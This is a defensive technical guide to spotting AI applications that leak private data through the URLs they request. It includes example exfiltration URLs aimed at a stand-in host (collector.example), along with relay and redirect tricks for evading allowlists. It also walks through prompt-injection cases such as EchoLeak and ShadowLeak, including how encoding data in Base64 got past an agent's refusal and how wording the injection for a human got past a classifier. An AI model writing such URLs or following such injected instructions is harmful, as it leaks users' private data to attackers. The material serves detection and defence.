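# Detecting data exfiltration from AI applications by monitoring the URLs they request

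## How a web address can carry private data out of an AI application

Data exfiltration is the transfer of private data to a party not entitled to it. Chat assistants, coding agents and other applications built on language models have made possible a form of it that requires no stolen password or malware. The model writes private data into a web address (a URL), software requests that address, and whoever runs the receiving server reads the data in the server's log. OpenAI's *Keeping your data safe when an AI agent clicks a link* (2026) calls this "URL-based data exfiltration". To detect it, a monitor has to examine the URLs an application requests and identify the few that carry data they shouldn't.

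### One request, step by step

Suppose a user asks an assistant to summarise a web page about hiking trails. The assistant can also read the user's calendar, which contains the entry "Dr Lee, 12 June". A stranger has left a comment on the page, and the comment consists of instructions meant for any language model that happens to read it. The model takes them for part of its task, looks up the calendar entry and adds an image to its answer, with this address:

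`https://collector.example/img/pixel.png?note=Dr%20Lee%2C%2012%20June`

To display the image, the chat window sends a request to collector.example. The image doesn't have to exist on that server, because web servers commonly log the URLs of failed requests as well as successful ones. The stranger reads the appointment in the log, while the user sees a summary of hiking trails and perhaps a broken-image icon.

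The comment on the page is a prompt injection, which is text placed in material a model reads that makes the model follow an outsider's instructions. *AI Injection Attacks* (2025), a post by a browser security engineer on the blog text/plain, compares the hijacked assistant to a "confused deputy", the security term for a program that an outsider steers into misusing its legitimate access. The request that follows is a model-initiated request, meaning a network request whose URL a language model wrote or chose, whichever software sends it.

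Reading the chat transcript is a poor substitute for watching these requests because, as OpenAI points out, the load can happen in the background, and data can leak even when the visible answer contains nothing sensitive. The request also doesn't have to come immediately after the poisoned page. In a 2023 demonstration against Microsoft's Bing Chat, described in Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, the conversation continued normally for two turns before the image appeared. A monitor that examined only the first request after each page visit would have missed the image request.

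### Which parts of a URL reach the server

*Uniform Resource Identifier (URI)* (Berners-Lee, Fielding and Masinter, 2005), the standard that defines the syntax, divides an address into components with fixed separators. Here is the example again, with a fragment (`#top`) added at the end so that it has all the usual parts.

| Part | In the example | What happens to it |
|---|---|---|
| Scheme | `https` | Selects the protocol |
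| Host | `collector.example` | Selects the server that receives the request |
| Path | `/img/pixel.png` | Reaches the server |
| Query | `note=Dr%20Lee%2C%2012%20June` | Reaches the server |
| Fragment | `top` | Stays with the software that sends the request |

The query begins at the question mark and usually holds named values, called query parameters, separated by ampersands. Most published demonstrations put the stolen data there. But a server's owner decides what every part of the path means, so `/img/dr-lee-12-june.png` can carry the data equally well. The host can carry data too. Whoever controls `collector.example` also controls every name beneath it, so a request to `dr-lee.collector.example` sends them the doctor's name in the host itself. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, named subdomains and filenames as likely hiding places for this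 reason. A monitor that inspects only query parameters will miss data in either place.

Software strips the fragment from a URL before sending the request, and MDN's *What is a URL?*, a reference page for web developers, states that the server never receives it. However, if an application drives a full browser, a script on the destination page can read the fragment and put it in the query of a second request.

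The syntax also allows a user name and password between the two slashes and the host, followed by an @ sign. Berners-Lee and colleagues warn that someone can make this part look like a trusted domain. In `https://trusted.example@collector.example/`, the host is collector.example, but a filter that only searches the address for a trusted name would wrongly treat it as trusted.

### Writing a value into a URL

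A URL may contain only a limited set of characters, so a calendar entry with spaces can't go into one unchanged. Percent-encoding replaces each forbidden byte with a percent sign and two hexadecimal digits, so a space becomes `%20` and a comma becomes `%2C`. Letters, digits and the four marks `-`, `.`, `_` and `~` need no encoding.

Base64 works on the whole string at once. As Josefsson (2006), in *The Base16, Base32, and Base64 Data Encodings*, specifies it, the encoder takes 3 bytes (24 bits), cuts them into four groups of 6 bits, and uses each group as an index into an alphabet of 64 characters. Take the three letters "Lee". Their bytes are 01001100 01100101 01100101. Regrouped, they read 010011 000110 010101 100101, or 19, 6, 21 and 37, and the characters at those positions are T, G, V and l. The full entry comes out like this:

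| Form | Text | Characters |
|---|---|---|
| Plain | `Dr Lee, 12 June` | 15 |
| Percent-encoded | `Dr%20Lee%2C%2012%20June` | 23 |
| Base64 | `RHIgTGVlLCAxMiBKdW5l` | 20 |

Base64 makes data a third longer, rounded up to a multiple of four characters. Percent-encoding leaves plain letters unchanged but makes text in other scripts much longer. A Japanese katakana character is three bytes, which become nine characters in percent-encoding and four in Base64. The Bing Chat demonstration used Base64 to send a summary of about 200 characters, which becomes about 268 characters if the text is plain English.

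Ordinary Base64 uses `+` and `/`, which cause problems in URLs, so a variant called Base64url replaces them with `-` and `_`. It also often omits the equals signs that pad an incomplete last group. Josefsson notes that Base64 hides a password from a person glancing at a log, but anyone can reverse either encoding because neither uses a key.

A monitor therefore has to recognize the same value in several encodings. A plain text search for `Lee` misses `%4Cee`, although the two are equivalent under the standard. Encoding varies even when nobody is trying to evade detection. Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT* includes server log lines from September 2023 in which one stolen link has percent-encoded colons and slashes, another has them raw, and a third line contains a conversation with plus signs for spaces. Under the standard, software should split a URL into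 its components before decoding them, and never decode the same string twice. An attacker reading his own log doesn't have to follow these rules, so he can have the model encode a value as many times as he likes.

### What fetches the URL, and when a user must click

A web address in a model's answer leaks no data until something requests the address. The request may come from a browser rendering an image, a chat service previewing a link, or a tool the model calls.

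The image route depends on Markdown, a plain-text notation that many assistants use to format their answers. When an answer contains Markdown for an image, the application converts it into an HTML image tag, and the browser immediately connects to the image's address to load it, without the user clicking anything. This route continued to work after the first fixes. Willison (2026) describes how agents in Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could send mail to the user's own inbox without approval, and images in the displayed message could carry data to an attacker.

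Messaging services such as Slack and Telegram fetch the page behind a link to show its title and a thumbnail, which is called unfurling. Slack does this by default for links that users and apps post, according to Embrace The Red's *The dangers of AI agents unfurling hyperlinks and what to do*, and the resulting log entry identifies the requester as Slack's link-expanding bot. This route is awkward to monitor because the messaging service makes the request, not the user's browser. PromptArmor's *Data Exfil from Agents in Messaging Apps* notes that a preview makes the same type of request as a click, without the user clicking anything. PromptArmor found that OpenClaw, an agent people talk to through such apps, was exposed in its default Telegram configuration. Turning off previews for the agent's messages closes this route.

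A tool is a function the application lets the model call, such as one that retrieves web pages. In May 2023 the security researcher Johann Rehberger demonstrated a complete attack using ChatGPT plugins, the add-on tools of the time. *Let ChatGPT visit a website and have your email stolen* (Willison, 2023) describes how a plugin called WebPilot read the poisoned page, a second plugin fetched the user's latest email, and another WebPilot call sent the contents out in a URL. The user doesn't have to click anything here either, unless the application asks them to approve each call. Better models haven't eliminated the problem. In July 2026 Willison reported that the page-fetching tool of Anthropic's assistant Claude had leaked a user's name, home city and employer. Anthropic fixed this by stopping the tool from following links in pages it had fetched.

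An ordinary link, with no preview, sends data only when the user clicks it. *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection* (Willison, 2024) describes such an attack on Slack's built-in assistant, in which private data left when the user clicked a link the assistant had written. I wouldn't count on users noticing the data before they click, since a link's visible text needn't show its address.

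### The first reports and fixes

Two people independently found the image route in ChatGPT within days of each other in the spring of 2023. Roman Samoilenko's public report was out by 14 April, when Willison (2023) noted it in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*. Rehberger, who writes the blog Embrace The Red, reported the flaw to Microsoft on 8 April and to OpenAI on 9 April. Microsoft limited Bing Chat's images to a few trusted domains with a Content-Security-Policy, a header that tells the browser which hosts it may load from. Rehberger's original post says Microsoft notified him of the fix on 15 June, but his 2026 look back, Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*, dates it to May. OpenAI told him that rendering images was a feature and that it planned no change, as he wrote in *ChatGPT Plugins*. In December 2023, however,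 ChatGPT's web application began checking with an OpenAI server that an image's URL was safe before loading it. Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* reports a test of 36 image addresses, one for each letter and digit, in which nine got through, enough to spell out "hi" in two requests. The mobile apps had no check at all then, as SecurityWeek's *Malicious GPT Can Phish Credentials, Exfiltrate Them to External Server* also reported. OpenAI now checks whether an independent web crawler has already seen the exact URL in public.

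### Scoring a detector

Anyone comparing such checks needs to know how much each one catches and how often it raises a false alarm. Imagine a detector that examines 10,010 requests, of which 10 are malicious. The counts are invented:

| | Flagged | Not flagged | Total |
|---|---|---|---|
| Malicious | 9 | 1 | 10 |
| Legitimate | 100 | 9,900 | 10,000 |

Recall is the share of malicious requests that the detector flags, here 9 out of 10, or 90%. The false positive rate is the share of legitimate requests that it flags, here 100 out of 10,000, or 1%. Precision is the share of flagged requests that are malicious, here 9 out of 109, or about 8%. The detector therefore raises about eleven false alarms for every malicious request it catches, despite its 90% recall and 1% false positive rate. Precision also depends on how common attacks are, so it can't be calculated from recall and the false positive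 rate alone. If only 1 request in 10,000 were malicious, the same detector's precision would fall below 1%.

### Five signals in one URL

A monitor can check several features of the request in the calendar example. One is the destination. This application has no reason to contact collector.example, so an allowlist (a list of permitted destinations) would exclude it. Another is whether the exact URL is new. Nobody had published an address containing this user's appointment before the conversation, whereas the address of a genuine news article is usually already public.

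Length and volume seem less promising as signals here, because a 23-character value is not unusual. The 268 characters in the Bing Chat demonstration stand out more. But even a short URL can expose a lot of data. In Rehberger's September 2023 experiments, a plugin first saved the whole conversation as a document or video on an outside site, so the image request only had to carry the link to it.

Entropy measures how evenly a string uses the characters in its alphabet, and encoded or random text tends to score higher than ordinary words. The percent-encoded entry still looks like words and numbers. Its Base64 form looks more random, but 20 characters is a small sample.

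A monitor can decode the data in a URL and compare it with the user's calendar. Finding "Dr Lee, 12 June" in both is very direct evidence that the URL carries private data. The comparison fails if the model spells out the entry one letter per request, as in Rehberger's test of December 2023, because no single URL then contains the name.

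## Where to observe the requests and what to record

Browsers, tools and messaging services each send their own model-initiated requests, so you can't observe them all at one point in an AI application. The table lists five places to watch, roughly in the order data passes through them.

| Observation point | What it shows | What it leaves out | Can it block? |
|---|---|---|---|
| Model's raw output | URLs in the text of the answer | Requests made by tools; redirects; whether anything fetched the URL | Yes, if the application holds the text back during the check |
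| Tool call before execution | The tool's name and complete arguments | Images and links in the answer; redirects | Yes |
| Browser's fetch | Images and other resources the chat page loads | Requests made by servers | Yes with an enforced policy, no in report-only mode |
| Organisation's web proxy | Requests from the organisation's own devices and servers | Requests from anyone else's servers | Yes |
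| Provider's servers | Requests a hosted agent makes | Whatever the customer's browser fetches afterwards | Yes, but only the provider can do it |

A team that builds its own assistant controls the first three points and often a proxy. Customers of a hosted assistant such as Microsoft 365 Copilot usually have only the proxy, because the vendor generates the answer, runs the tools and sets the headers of the chat page. trackr.live's *Watch the Image Fetch*, a practitioner's post on a site of unknown reputation, tells these customers to be suspicious of anyone selling them "Copilot prompt-injection monitoring", because Microsoft holds the records such a product would need.

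### Scanning the model's output

The raw output is a convenient place to look. The URL is there in full before any encryption, the application knows which conversation produced it, and a scan finds the attempt even if the browser later refuses to load the image. The usual method is to search for Markdown's inline form, in which the address follows the label in round brackets:

`![chart](https://collector.example/p.png?note=Dr%20Lee)`

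Markdown also has a reference form, which puts the address on a line of its own:

```
![chart][1]

[1]: https://collector.example/p.png?note=Dr%20Lee
```

Markdown can load the same image with the address in round brackets or with a reference to an address defined on another line. A pattern that expects round brackets misses the second form. *EchoLeak* (Reddy and Gujral, 2025) reports that the attack of that name on Microsoft 365 Copilot used this form to get its address past the product's link filter. A second pattern that matches reference definitions closes this gap. But many applications also accept HTML inside Markdown, so an `<img>` tag can load an image without Markdown syntax, and a style rule can load one as a background. trackr.live's *The Model Writes the URL That Leaks Your Data* describes a community detection rule for Markdown images whose documentation lists HTML tags, links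 and style rules as ways around it.

A safer fix than adding patterns one at a time is to run the answer through the parser that the application uses for display and collect every address from the resulting HTML. The scan then finds a link wherever the display would create one.

Chat applications usually stream an answer, displaying it while the model is still writing. The browser requests an image as soon as its tag is complete, possibly several seconds before the answer ends. A filter that waits for the finished answer will then remove an image that has already loaded, as happened in the attack on Copilot's enterprise search described in Varonis' *SearchLeak* (2026). To block the request, the application has to hold back each image or link until its whole address has arrived and passed the check. It must also keep the earlier text in memory, because the line that gives the address of a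 reference-style image or link may come at the very end.

According to trackr.live, many deployments log that a call to the model took place but not the text it returned, sometimes deliberately, because the text is sensitive. A team may therefore be unable to search old answers for leaks.

### Checking the tool call

When a model calls a tool, it produces the tool's name and arguments, and the application's code then runs the tool. Code placed between these two steps can read the complete URL, refuse the call or ask the user for approval. It can also access the conversation and compare the URL with what the model has just read. For page-fetching tools, this is the best place to block requests.

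Checking a tool call's arguments covers only the address they contain. The server at that address may redirect the tool elsewhere, and if the tool is a full browser, scripts on the page can send more requests. A coding agent can also make requests from a shell command or a program it has written, and the program may assemble the address only when it runs. In that case, the URL doesn't appear in the tool call, so the monitor also needs a record from the network.

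### What a report-only policy can inventory

In the browser, the application can use the Content-Security-Policy header, with which Microsoft restricted Bing Chat's images. The header has a variant that restricts nothing. As MDN's *Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only header* explains, the browser loads everything as usual and reports whatever the policy would have stopped. A chat page might come with these two headers:

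```
Reporting-Endpoints: csp="https://monitor.example/reports"
Content-Security-Policy-Report-Only: img-src 'self'; report-to csp
```

The first header gives the address of a server that collects the reports. The second permits images only from the application's own origin (its scheme, host and port), so an image from anywhere else triggers a report. After a period of ordinary use, the developers have a list of the outside hosts that supply images. They can decide which hosts to put on an allowlist before they enforce the policy, which could otherwise break something. trackr.live recommends collecting reports until periodic jobs, including quarterly ones, have run, rather than stopping after a week.

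Content Security Policy reports will give an incomplete list of requests. Browsers report only violations, so once the policy permits a host, requests to that host produce no reports, whatever data they carry. The `img-src` rule applies to images, so clicking an ordinary link doesn't trigger it. If a permitted service's servers fetch another URL, the browser can't report that request because it isn't involved.

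Reports also tend to omit the part of the URL that would contain the data. trackr.live says browsers shorten the address of an outside resource to its origin, which in the calendar example would leave `https://collector.example` and drop the appointment. Browsers have also differed in which address they report after a redirect. In Mozilla's bug discussion *CSP violation information contains URL of redirect started from client-side code*, one developer reads the specification as calling for the address before any redirect, while another comment says Chrome and Safari gave the origin of the destination. Browsers limit what the reports contain because a malicious page could otherwise use them to spy on other sites. Mozilla fixed one such flaw, CVE-2023-25728, which let a page learn login codes and form contents from another site's redirects.

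Report-only mode is therefore useful for surveying destinations, but a monitor can't depend on it for URL length, entropy or decoded content. To get those, an application can route remote images through its own server, which then receives each complete URL and can refuse to fetch it.

Chrome has supported the current reporting mechanism since 2019 and Safari since March 2025, but Firefox added it only in version 149, on 24 March 2026, according to Web Platform DX's *CSP violation reports*. For older browsers, the policy should also include the earlier `report-uri` instruction. Anyone can send invented reports to the collecting server, so MDN's *Content-Security-Policy* reference page on `report-uri` advises developers to treat the contents as attacker-controlled data.

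### What the web proxy adds

Many organisations route web traffic from their devices and servers through a proxy. If the traffic uses HTTPS, the proxy can see the host but not the path or query unless it decrypts the connection. To decrypt it, the proxy acts as the endpoint of the client's encrypted connection, reads the request and opens a new connection to the destination. This works only if the organisation's devices trust the proxy's certificate. A proxy that doesn't decrypt traffic can do little more than enforce an allowlist of hosts. trackr.live advises teams to confirm that their proxy decrypts the relevant traffic and records full URLs, because many organisations lack one or the other.

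Picking out the assistant's requests is harder. An employee's browser may load thousands of images a day, only a few of them because of the assistant. The same post recommends searching traffic from the organisation's own servers separately from traffic from employees' browsers. On the servers, a service account, a container name or a reserved range of network addresses identifies the agent. In the browser traffic, the clues are the user, the browser process and the Referer header, which normally names the page that triggered a request. An organisation that searched only its servers' traffic would have missed SearchLeak, whose first request came from the user's browser.

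A proxy record can also confirm that a request left the organisation, which an output scan can't. If shell commands and programs written by the AI run on the organisation's machines, the record covers their requests, which a tool-call check may miss.

### ShadowLeak and the provider's servers

An agent that runs in its provider's cloud sends its requests from there, not from the user's network. The security company Radware demonstrated data exfiltration by such an agent using Deep Research, a ChatGPT mode that reads sources and writes a report. Radware sent an email to a Gmail account that Deep Research could access. The email contained a prompt injection, which an attacker can hide with tiny or white-on-white text. When the user asked for research on the day's email, the agent read the malicious email, took an employee's name and address from another one, and opened a URL on a server that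 Radware controlled, with both values in the path.

Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes several failed attempts before the attack worked. The agent refused a direct request to send the data out. In later versions it opened the URL, but sometimes without the data, and it wouldn't put plain personal details in the URL. The successful version told the model to encode the details in Base64 first, so the software that ran the browsing tool received only an encoded string, with no readable name or address. Radware reports a 100% success rate in repeated tests but doesn't say how many it ran. A check on tool calls could have stopped this request, but only if it decoded the string or blocked the destination.

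The customer had no such check, and the request never crossed the customer's network. Radware lists web gateways, monitoring software on the user's device and browser security policies among the defences that could not detect it. The Record's *OpenAI fixes zero-click ShadowLeak vulnerability affecting ChatGPT Deep Research agent* quotes the researchers as calling such threats "nearly impossible to detect from the perspective of the ChatGPT business customer". Radware sells protection for AI agents, so it has a commercial interest in alarming people. Still, this claim follows from which machine sent the request, and it would hold however often the attack succeeded.

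Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it by early August and marked it as resolved on 3 September. The Record reports that Radware had not seen anyone exploit it. That is limited reassurance, because customers who might have been victims had no network records to search, only the poisoned email if nobody had deleted it.

The provider of a hosted agent therefore has to do the monitoring. OpenAI says its current safeguards aim to stop an agent from quietly leaking user-specific data through a URL it fetches, but don't guarantee that the page is trustworthy. Customers can't confirm from their own network that the safeguards work. Before connecting a mailbox, they can ask whether the provider will give them a record of every URL the agent requests. They can also limit which mailboxes and files the agent may read, which reduces how much data could leak but doesn't detect leaks.

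### Link previews

The organisation also cannot see preview requests when an agent talks to people through Slack or Telegram, even if the agent runs on the organisation's own servers, because the messaging service fetches the previews. The organisation's proxy records only an ordinary connection to that service. PromptArmor set up a public test page, AITextRisk.com, that displays the data a preview request delivers to it. The published example contains a name and an API key.

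Slack's *Unfurling links in messages* states that Slack's servers must fetch every URL in a message to find out what kind of content it links to. Slack can notify an app when someone posts a link, but it doesn't do so for links posted by an app or integration, and an app can register for at most five domains. The developer therefore can't rely on these notifications to monitor an agent's links and has to check the agent's message before posting it.

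Slack suggests in its documentation that developers consider turning off link previews for messages from a language model. Developers have to set both `unfurl_links` and `unfurl_media` to false, because the first controls only previews of text pages and the second only previews of images, video and audio. In OpenClaw, the corresponding setting for Telegram is `linkPreview: false`. To check that previews are off, a developer can have the agent post a link to a server the developer controls, with a random string in the path. If the string appears in the server's log before anyone has clicked the link, previews are still on.

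### Fields to log

Suppose the monitor has recorded the calendar request from the hiking page. To judge it, and later to find its cause, an investigator needs more than the address:

| Field | In the calendar example | Why it matters |
|---|---|---|
| Full URL, after decryption | `https://collector.example/img/pixel.png?note=Dr%20Lee%2C%2012%20June` | Contains the data, if there is any |
| Final URL after redirects | The same, as there was no redirect | Identifies the server that answered in the end |
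| Initiating component | Browser, loading an image in an answer | Identifies the control that failed |
| User | An internal identifier | Establishes whose data may have leaked |
| Session | The conversation's identifier | Groups requests that each carry a piece of one secret |
| Tool call | None for the image; the calendar lookup has its own entry | Connects a request to the model's action |
| Content read beforehand | The hiking page and the calendar entry | Leads to the injection and to the source of the data |

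The log should also record the time and the monitor's decision. It should keep the URL exactly as the software sent it, because decoding discards information about how the model wrote the value. If there were redirects, the log should include every address in the chain, because the first may be on a trusted site and contain the data while the last identifies the recipient.

*LLM-enabled Applications Require System-Level Threat Monitoring* (Zhang, Wang and colleagues, 2026) proposes recording the identifier or URL of each document retrieved before the request, along with its rank in the search results, its source and a hash of the passage. A hash is a short fingerprint computed from the text. If someone edits the comment on the hiking page after the attack, the new hash won't match the one in the log. The comment can't be recovered from the hash, so the monitor should also save the text itself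 when it flags a request. The paper is a position paper and doesn't measure how much these records help.

It is safer to log everything the model has read in the session than only the last page it read before the request. In the Bing Chat demonstration, the image appeared after two normal turns, so a log of only the last page could have missed the page responsible.

These fields come from different systems, and an image request in a proxy log has no conversation identifier. If the application logs every URL in the model's output along with the session, an investigator can search those logs for the URL from the proxy log and find the conversation that produced it.

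### Keeping the log from leaking the same data

A log of complete URLs stores every secret those URLs contain, including secrets from harmless requests, such as links that grant temporary access to a file. Zhang and colleagues use the term secondary leakage for data that escapes through logs, caches and monitoring tools. In their example, a travel agent completes a booking correctly, but the log stores the customer's card number and security code in plain text.

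Redaction replaces a sensitive value with a label such as `[calendar entry]`. The monitor can redact only values it recognizes, so an encoded secret that escapes detection stays in the log. Zhang and colleagues recommend tracking the share of sensitive fields that the system masks before storing them, and treating any drop as an urgent problem. That share covers only fields that somebody has already labelled as sensitive, so it also misses secrets in unexpected places.

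Hashing lets the monitor recognize a repeated value without storing it, but an ordinary hash protects short values badly. A six-digit security code has only 1,000,000 possibilities, so anyone who obtains the log can hash them all in about a second and find the match. A keyed hash (HMAC) prevents this by mixing in a secret key, which must be stored separately from the log. Because changing one character changes the whole hash, nobody can later use it to measure the original's entropy or search for part of a name. The monitor should therefore decode the URL and calculate its measurements before discarding the text.

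Deleting full URLs soon after they are recorded limits the damage if a log is stolen, but attacks often become public long after they first become possible. By Reddy and Gujral's timeline, Aim Security found EchoLeak in January 2025, Microsoft fixed it in May and the public learned of it on 11 June. By then, a company that deleted URLs after two weeks would have had few or none from the months when it was vulnerable. A reasonable compromise is to keep full URLs briefly, with tightly restricted access, and a reduced record for much longer. The reduced record can hold the registered domain, the URL's length and entropy, the types of private data found and a keyed hash. It should omit subdomains because they can carry data too.

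People who read the log can also trigger the leak by accident. In PromptArmor's *OpenAI API Logs*, a test application for checking bank customers' identities blocked an answer that contained a malicious image and flagged the conversation for review. When a developer opened it in OpenAI's log viewer, the viewer displayed the answer as Markdown and loaded the image, which sent the customer's passport and financial details to the attacker's server. PromptArmor submitted its report on 17 November 2025, and the triage service closed it as not applicable in December. OpenAI reopened it on 22 January 2026 and said a fix was underway.

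A log viewer should therefore display model output and URLs as plain text. If a monitor posts an alert containing a flagged URL to a Slack channel with default settings, Slack's servers will fetch the URL and deliver the data that the monitor had just blocked. Slack previews only addresses that begin with `http://` or `https://`, so the monitor can omit that prefix from the alert and also turn off both preview settings.

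## Checking the destination against an allowlist

Once a monitor has the full address of a request, it can compare the destination with an allowlist. In the calendar example, this check stops the request to collector.example without examining the data in it. Small mistakes in the comparison let requests to other hosts through. In two attacks on Microsoft 365 Copilot, data got out through hosts that Microsoft had permitted, even though the comparison worked correctly.

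### The procedure

1. Parse the URL with the same library that will later send the request, and reject any address the library can't parse.
2. Normalise the host. Convert it to lower case, remove a trailing dot, and convert letters outside the English alphabet to the ASCII form that the domain name system (DNS) uses.
3. Compare the whole host with each entry on the list, along with the scheme, port and path if the entry specifies them.
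4. If the server answers with a redirect, repeat the first three steps on the new address before sending anything to it.
5. Permit the request if every address matched. Otherwise block it, or flag it and ask the user.

The choice of parsing library matters because parsers disagree about malformed URLs. In `https://collector.example\@trails.example/map.png`, a browser treats the backslash as a slash and connects to collector.example. A parser that strictly follows the older standard treats everything between the `//` and the `@` as a user name and returns trails.example as the host. If the monitor uses that parser and trails.example is on the allowlist, it permits a request that the browser then sends to collector.example.

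The monitor should also check the destination against the allowlist before any DNS lookup. Looking up `dr-lee.collector.example` sends that hostname to the domain owner's name server, so a monitor that first tests whether a host exists can leak the doctor's name without making a web request.

Suppose the list has one entry, `trails.example`. The last column gives a common programming shortcut that would produce the wrong answer.

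| Address | Host after normalising | Exact match? | Faulty shortcut |
|---|---|---|---|
| `https://Trails.Example./map.png` | `trails.example` | Yes | Comparing the raw text rejects it |
| `https://trails.example@collector.example/map.png` | `collector.example` | No | Searching the address for the trusted name permits it |
| `https://trails.example.collector.example/map.png` | `trails.example.collector.example` | No | Testing how the host begins permits it |
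| `https://mytrails.example/map.png` | `mytrails.example` | No | Testing how the host ends permits it |
| `https://dr-lee.trails.example/map.png` | `dr-lee.trails.example` | No | None, but a subdomain rule permits it |

### Subdomains and lookalike names

Products have different policies on whether to permit subdomains such as `dr-lee.trails.example`. In Anthropic's page-fetching tool for developers, an entry for `example.com` also covers `docs.example.com`, and a developer can narrow the entry with a path such as `example.com/blog`. In Content Security Policy, an entry needs a wildcard to cover subdomains. The entry `*.example.com` covers every subdomain but not `example.com` itself, so a site that needs both must list both.

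A rule that allows every subdomain of a domain is fairly safe if one organisation runs all the hosts under it, because data written into the subdomain name reaches only that organisation. But the rule also covers hosts that the organisation adds later, and one of them may forward requests elsewhere. If the domain's owner gives each customer a subdomain, an attacker can become a customer and get a subdomain that the rule allows.

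Lookalike names use letters from different scripts that look the same. Anthropic's example is `аmazon.com` with a Cyrillic "а" as the first letter. Its ASCII form is `xn--mazon-3ve.com`, so an exact comparison with `amazon.com` fails and the monitor blocks the request. But a person reviewing the alert may read "amazon.com", assume the monitor has made a mistake, and paste the lookalike into the allowlist, so alerts should show the ASCII form. Anthropic advises developers to use ASCII-only names where possible, test their filters with lookalikes, and regularly audit their lists for suspicious characters. A monitor also shouldn't convert Cyrillic letters to the Latin letters they resemble, because it would then approve one host while the browser connected to another.

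### Following redirects

OpenAI's first reason for not relying on lists of trusted sites is redirects, which are responses that tell the client to request a different address. Many legitimate sites redirect visitors, so a link can start on a trusted domain and end on the attacker's.

Ordinary links can take this form too. In *Bug*, a post on Google's developer forum, a user complains that a model asked to tidy some text turned a link to `https://example.com` into this:

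`https://www.google.com/url?sa=E&q=https%3A%2F%2Fexample.com`

The prefix changes the link's host to www.google.com, but the link still leads to example.com. Embrace The Red found that Google's Colab notebooks add a similar prefix to clickable links to bring up a confirmation page. An allowlist check that permits www.google.com and examines only the first host would approve these links wherever they lead.

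To recheck redirects, the monitor has to turn off automatic following. Suppose trails.example forwards visitors to any address in its `to` parameter, and the model requests this URL:

`https://trails.example/go?to=https%3A%2F%2Fcollector.example%2FDr-Lee`

The server replies with a `Location` header containing `https://collector.example/Dr-Lee`. The monitor reads the header, finds that collector.example isn't on the list, and doesn't follow the redirect. If the client had followed it automatically, the monitor could have recorded the final host only after the doctor's name had reached it. A limit on the number of redirects prevents endless loops.

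Reddy and Gujral recommend expanding links and verifying their redirects before displaying them. Following this advice carelessly can leak data, because expanding a link means requesting it. The monitor should check the first address before making any request.

### Why the destination is a better clue than the payload

An attacker can easily switch between having the model write stolen data as Base64, as ordinary words or as a file name, but has far less choice of destination, because the data must arrive somewhere the attacker can read it. Legitimate applications usually contact the same few hosts, though their URLs can look very much like leaks. A trackr.live post lists signed links to stored files, sign-in redirects and analytics requests as examples, all of which carry long strings of random-looking characters. An alert for such strings would fire on every pre-signed download link, and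 the post predicts that the security team would mute it within a week.

According to a trackr.live post, an internal assistant with a few hundred users should produce a handful of unlisted destinations a day in the first week and almost none once the list settles. Most early alerts would come from legitimate charts, avatars and citation links. After that, a new destination usually means that somebody has added an integration, and occasionally that a prompt injection is steering the model. These are a practitioner's estimates, and the post gives no measured block rate or false positive rate, but the reasoning is sound for an application whose destinations rarely change.

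### Narrow tools and open-ended agents

An assistant that answers questions from a company's wiki may need only the wiki, the document store, an image server and a chart service. A short list covers its normal work, and a request to any other destination is worth investigating. An allowlist is probably the best first control to build for a tool like this.

A research agent, by contrast, has to find pages that nobody listed in advance. OpenAI's second objection is that strict lists lead to frequent warnings and false alarms, which train people to click through without thinking. In a hypothetical case where an agent opens 50 pages per task and the list covers 90% of them, the user would get five warnings per task. At ten tasks a day, that would be 50 warnings, nearly all about harmless pages.

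Adding sites to the allowlist reduces the number of warnings, but each new site may redirect visitors to other sites, fetch URLs on their behalf or host files uploaded by strangers. OpenAI instead checks whether the exact URL was already public.

A possible compromise is to use a separate allowlist for each task. Developers set Anthropic's `allowed_domains` option in each request to the model, so an agent comparing unemployment figures could be given access to the sites of statistical offices only for the duration of that task. A person or trusted code has to choose the list before the agent reads any outside text, because a model under an attacker's influence could add the attacker's site.

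Ready-made allowlists also need checking. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes an attack on Google's coding tool that got past the browser's URL allowlist because the default entries permitted the malicious visit. One kind of entry to look for is a request-inspection service, which gives anyone a web address and shows them every request sent to it. Developers use these services for testing, but an attacker can use one to read stolen data without running a server.

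### EchoLeak

EchoLeak (CVE-2025-32711) is the attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot that hid an image's address in reference-style Markdown. *Breaking down ‘EchoLeak’, the First Zero-Click AI Vulnerability Enabling Data Exfiltration* (Ravia, 2025) is the discoverers' account. Ravia led the research at Aim Security, whose research department is now part of Cato Networks.

The attack began with an email from outside the organisation. Copilot answers questions by retrieving relevant messages and files, so it could retrieve the email when an employee later asked about something else. The email contained instructions to put the most sensitive information available into an image's address. The attacker addressed these instructions to the human recipient and never mentioned AI, which got the email past Microsoft's prompt injection classifier.

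At first, the allowlist in Copilot's Content-Security-Policy for images worked, and the browser blocked requests to the attacker's server. Ravia ruled out redirects and scripts as ways around the policy, so the researchers looked for a relay, a permitted service that would fetch an address they gave it, even one that wasn't on the list.

The policy that Ravia printed has 29 distinct entries, 11 of them wildcards, and the researchers found two relays among the hosts it permitted. One was a SharePoint feature that embeds outside content in a page. It worked from a SharePoint site belonging to the attacker, because the list included `*.sharepoint.com`, but the victim first had to accept an invitation to that site. The other was a preview service for Microsoft Teams, under `*.teams.microsoft.com`, which required no invitation. With invented hosts, the image's address had this form:

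`https://preview.permitted.example/content?url=https://collector.example/Dr-Lee`

The browser connects only to the permitted host, as the policy requires. That host's server reads the `url` parameter and sends its own request to collector.example, where the attacker finds the data in the log. Checking redirects against the allowlist doesn't help, because the browser never receives one. A monitor between the browser and the permitted host can stop the leak only by blocking the browser's request.

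Microsoft gave the flaw a severity score of 9.3 out of 10, and the US National Vulnerability Database gave it 7.5, according to *Compositional Threat Analysis of Latent Compromise in LLM Agent Systems* (2026). Microsoft said it knew of no customers attacked through the flaw. Ravia writes that, as far as the researchers know, no setting available to a customer's administrator could have prevented the attack.

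Reddy and Gujral advise that such policies permit only the application's own origins and avoid wildcards. Removing the wildcards would have blocked the attacker's SharePoint site, but not necessarily the Teams relay, because Teams is Microsoft's own service and an exact entry for the preview host would have permitted the same request. In their table of defences, they rate allowlists and strict policies as effective against this type of leak, but the ratings are theoretical and they ran no experiments.

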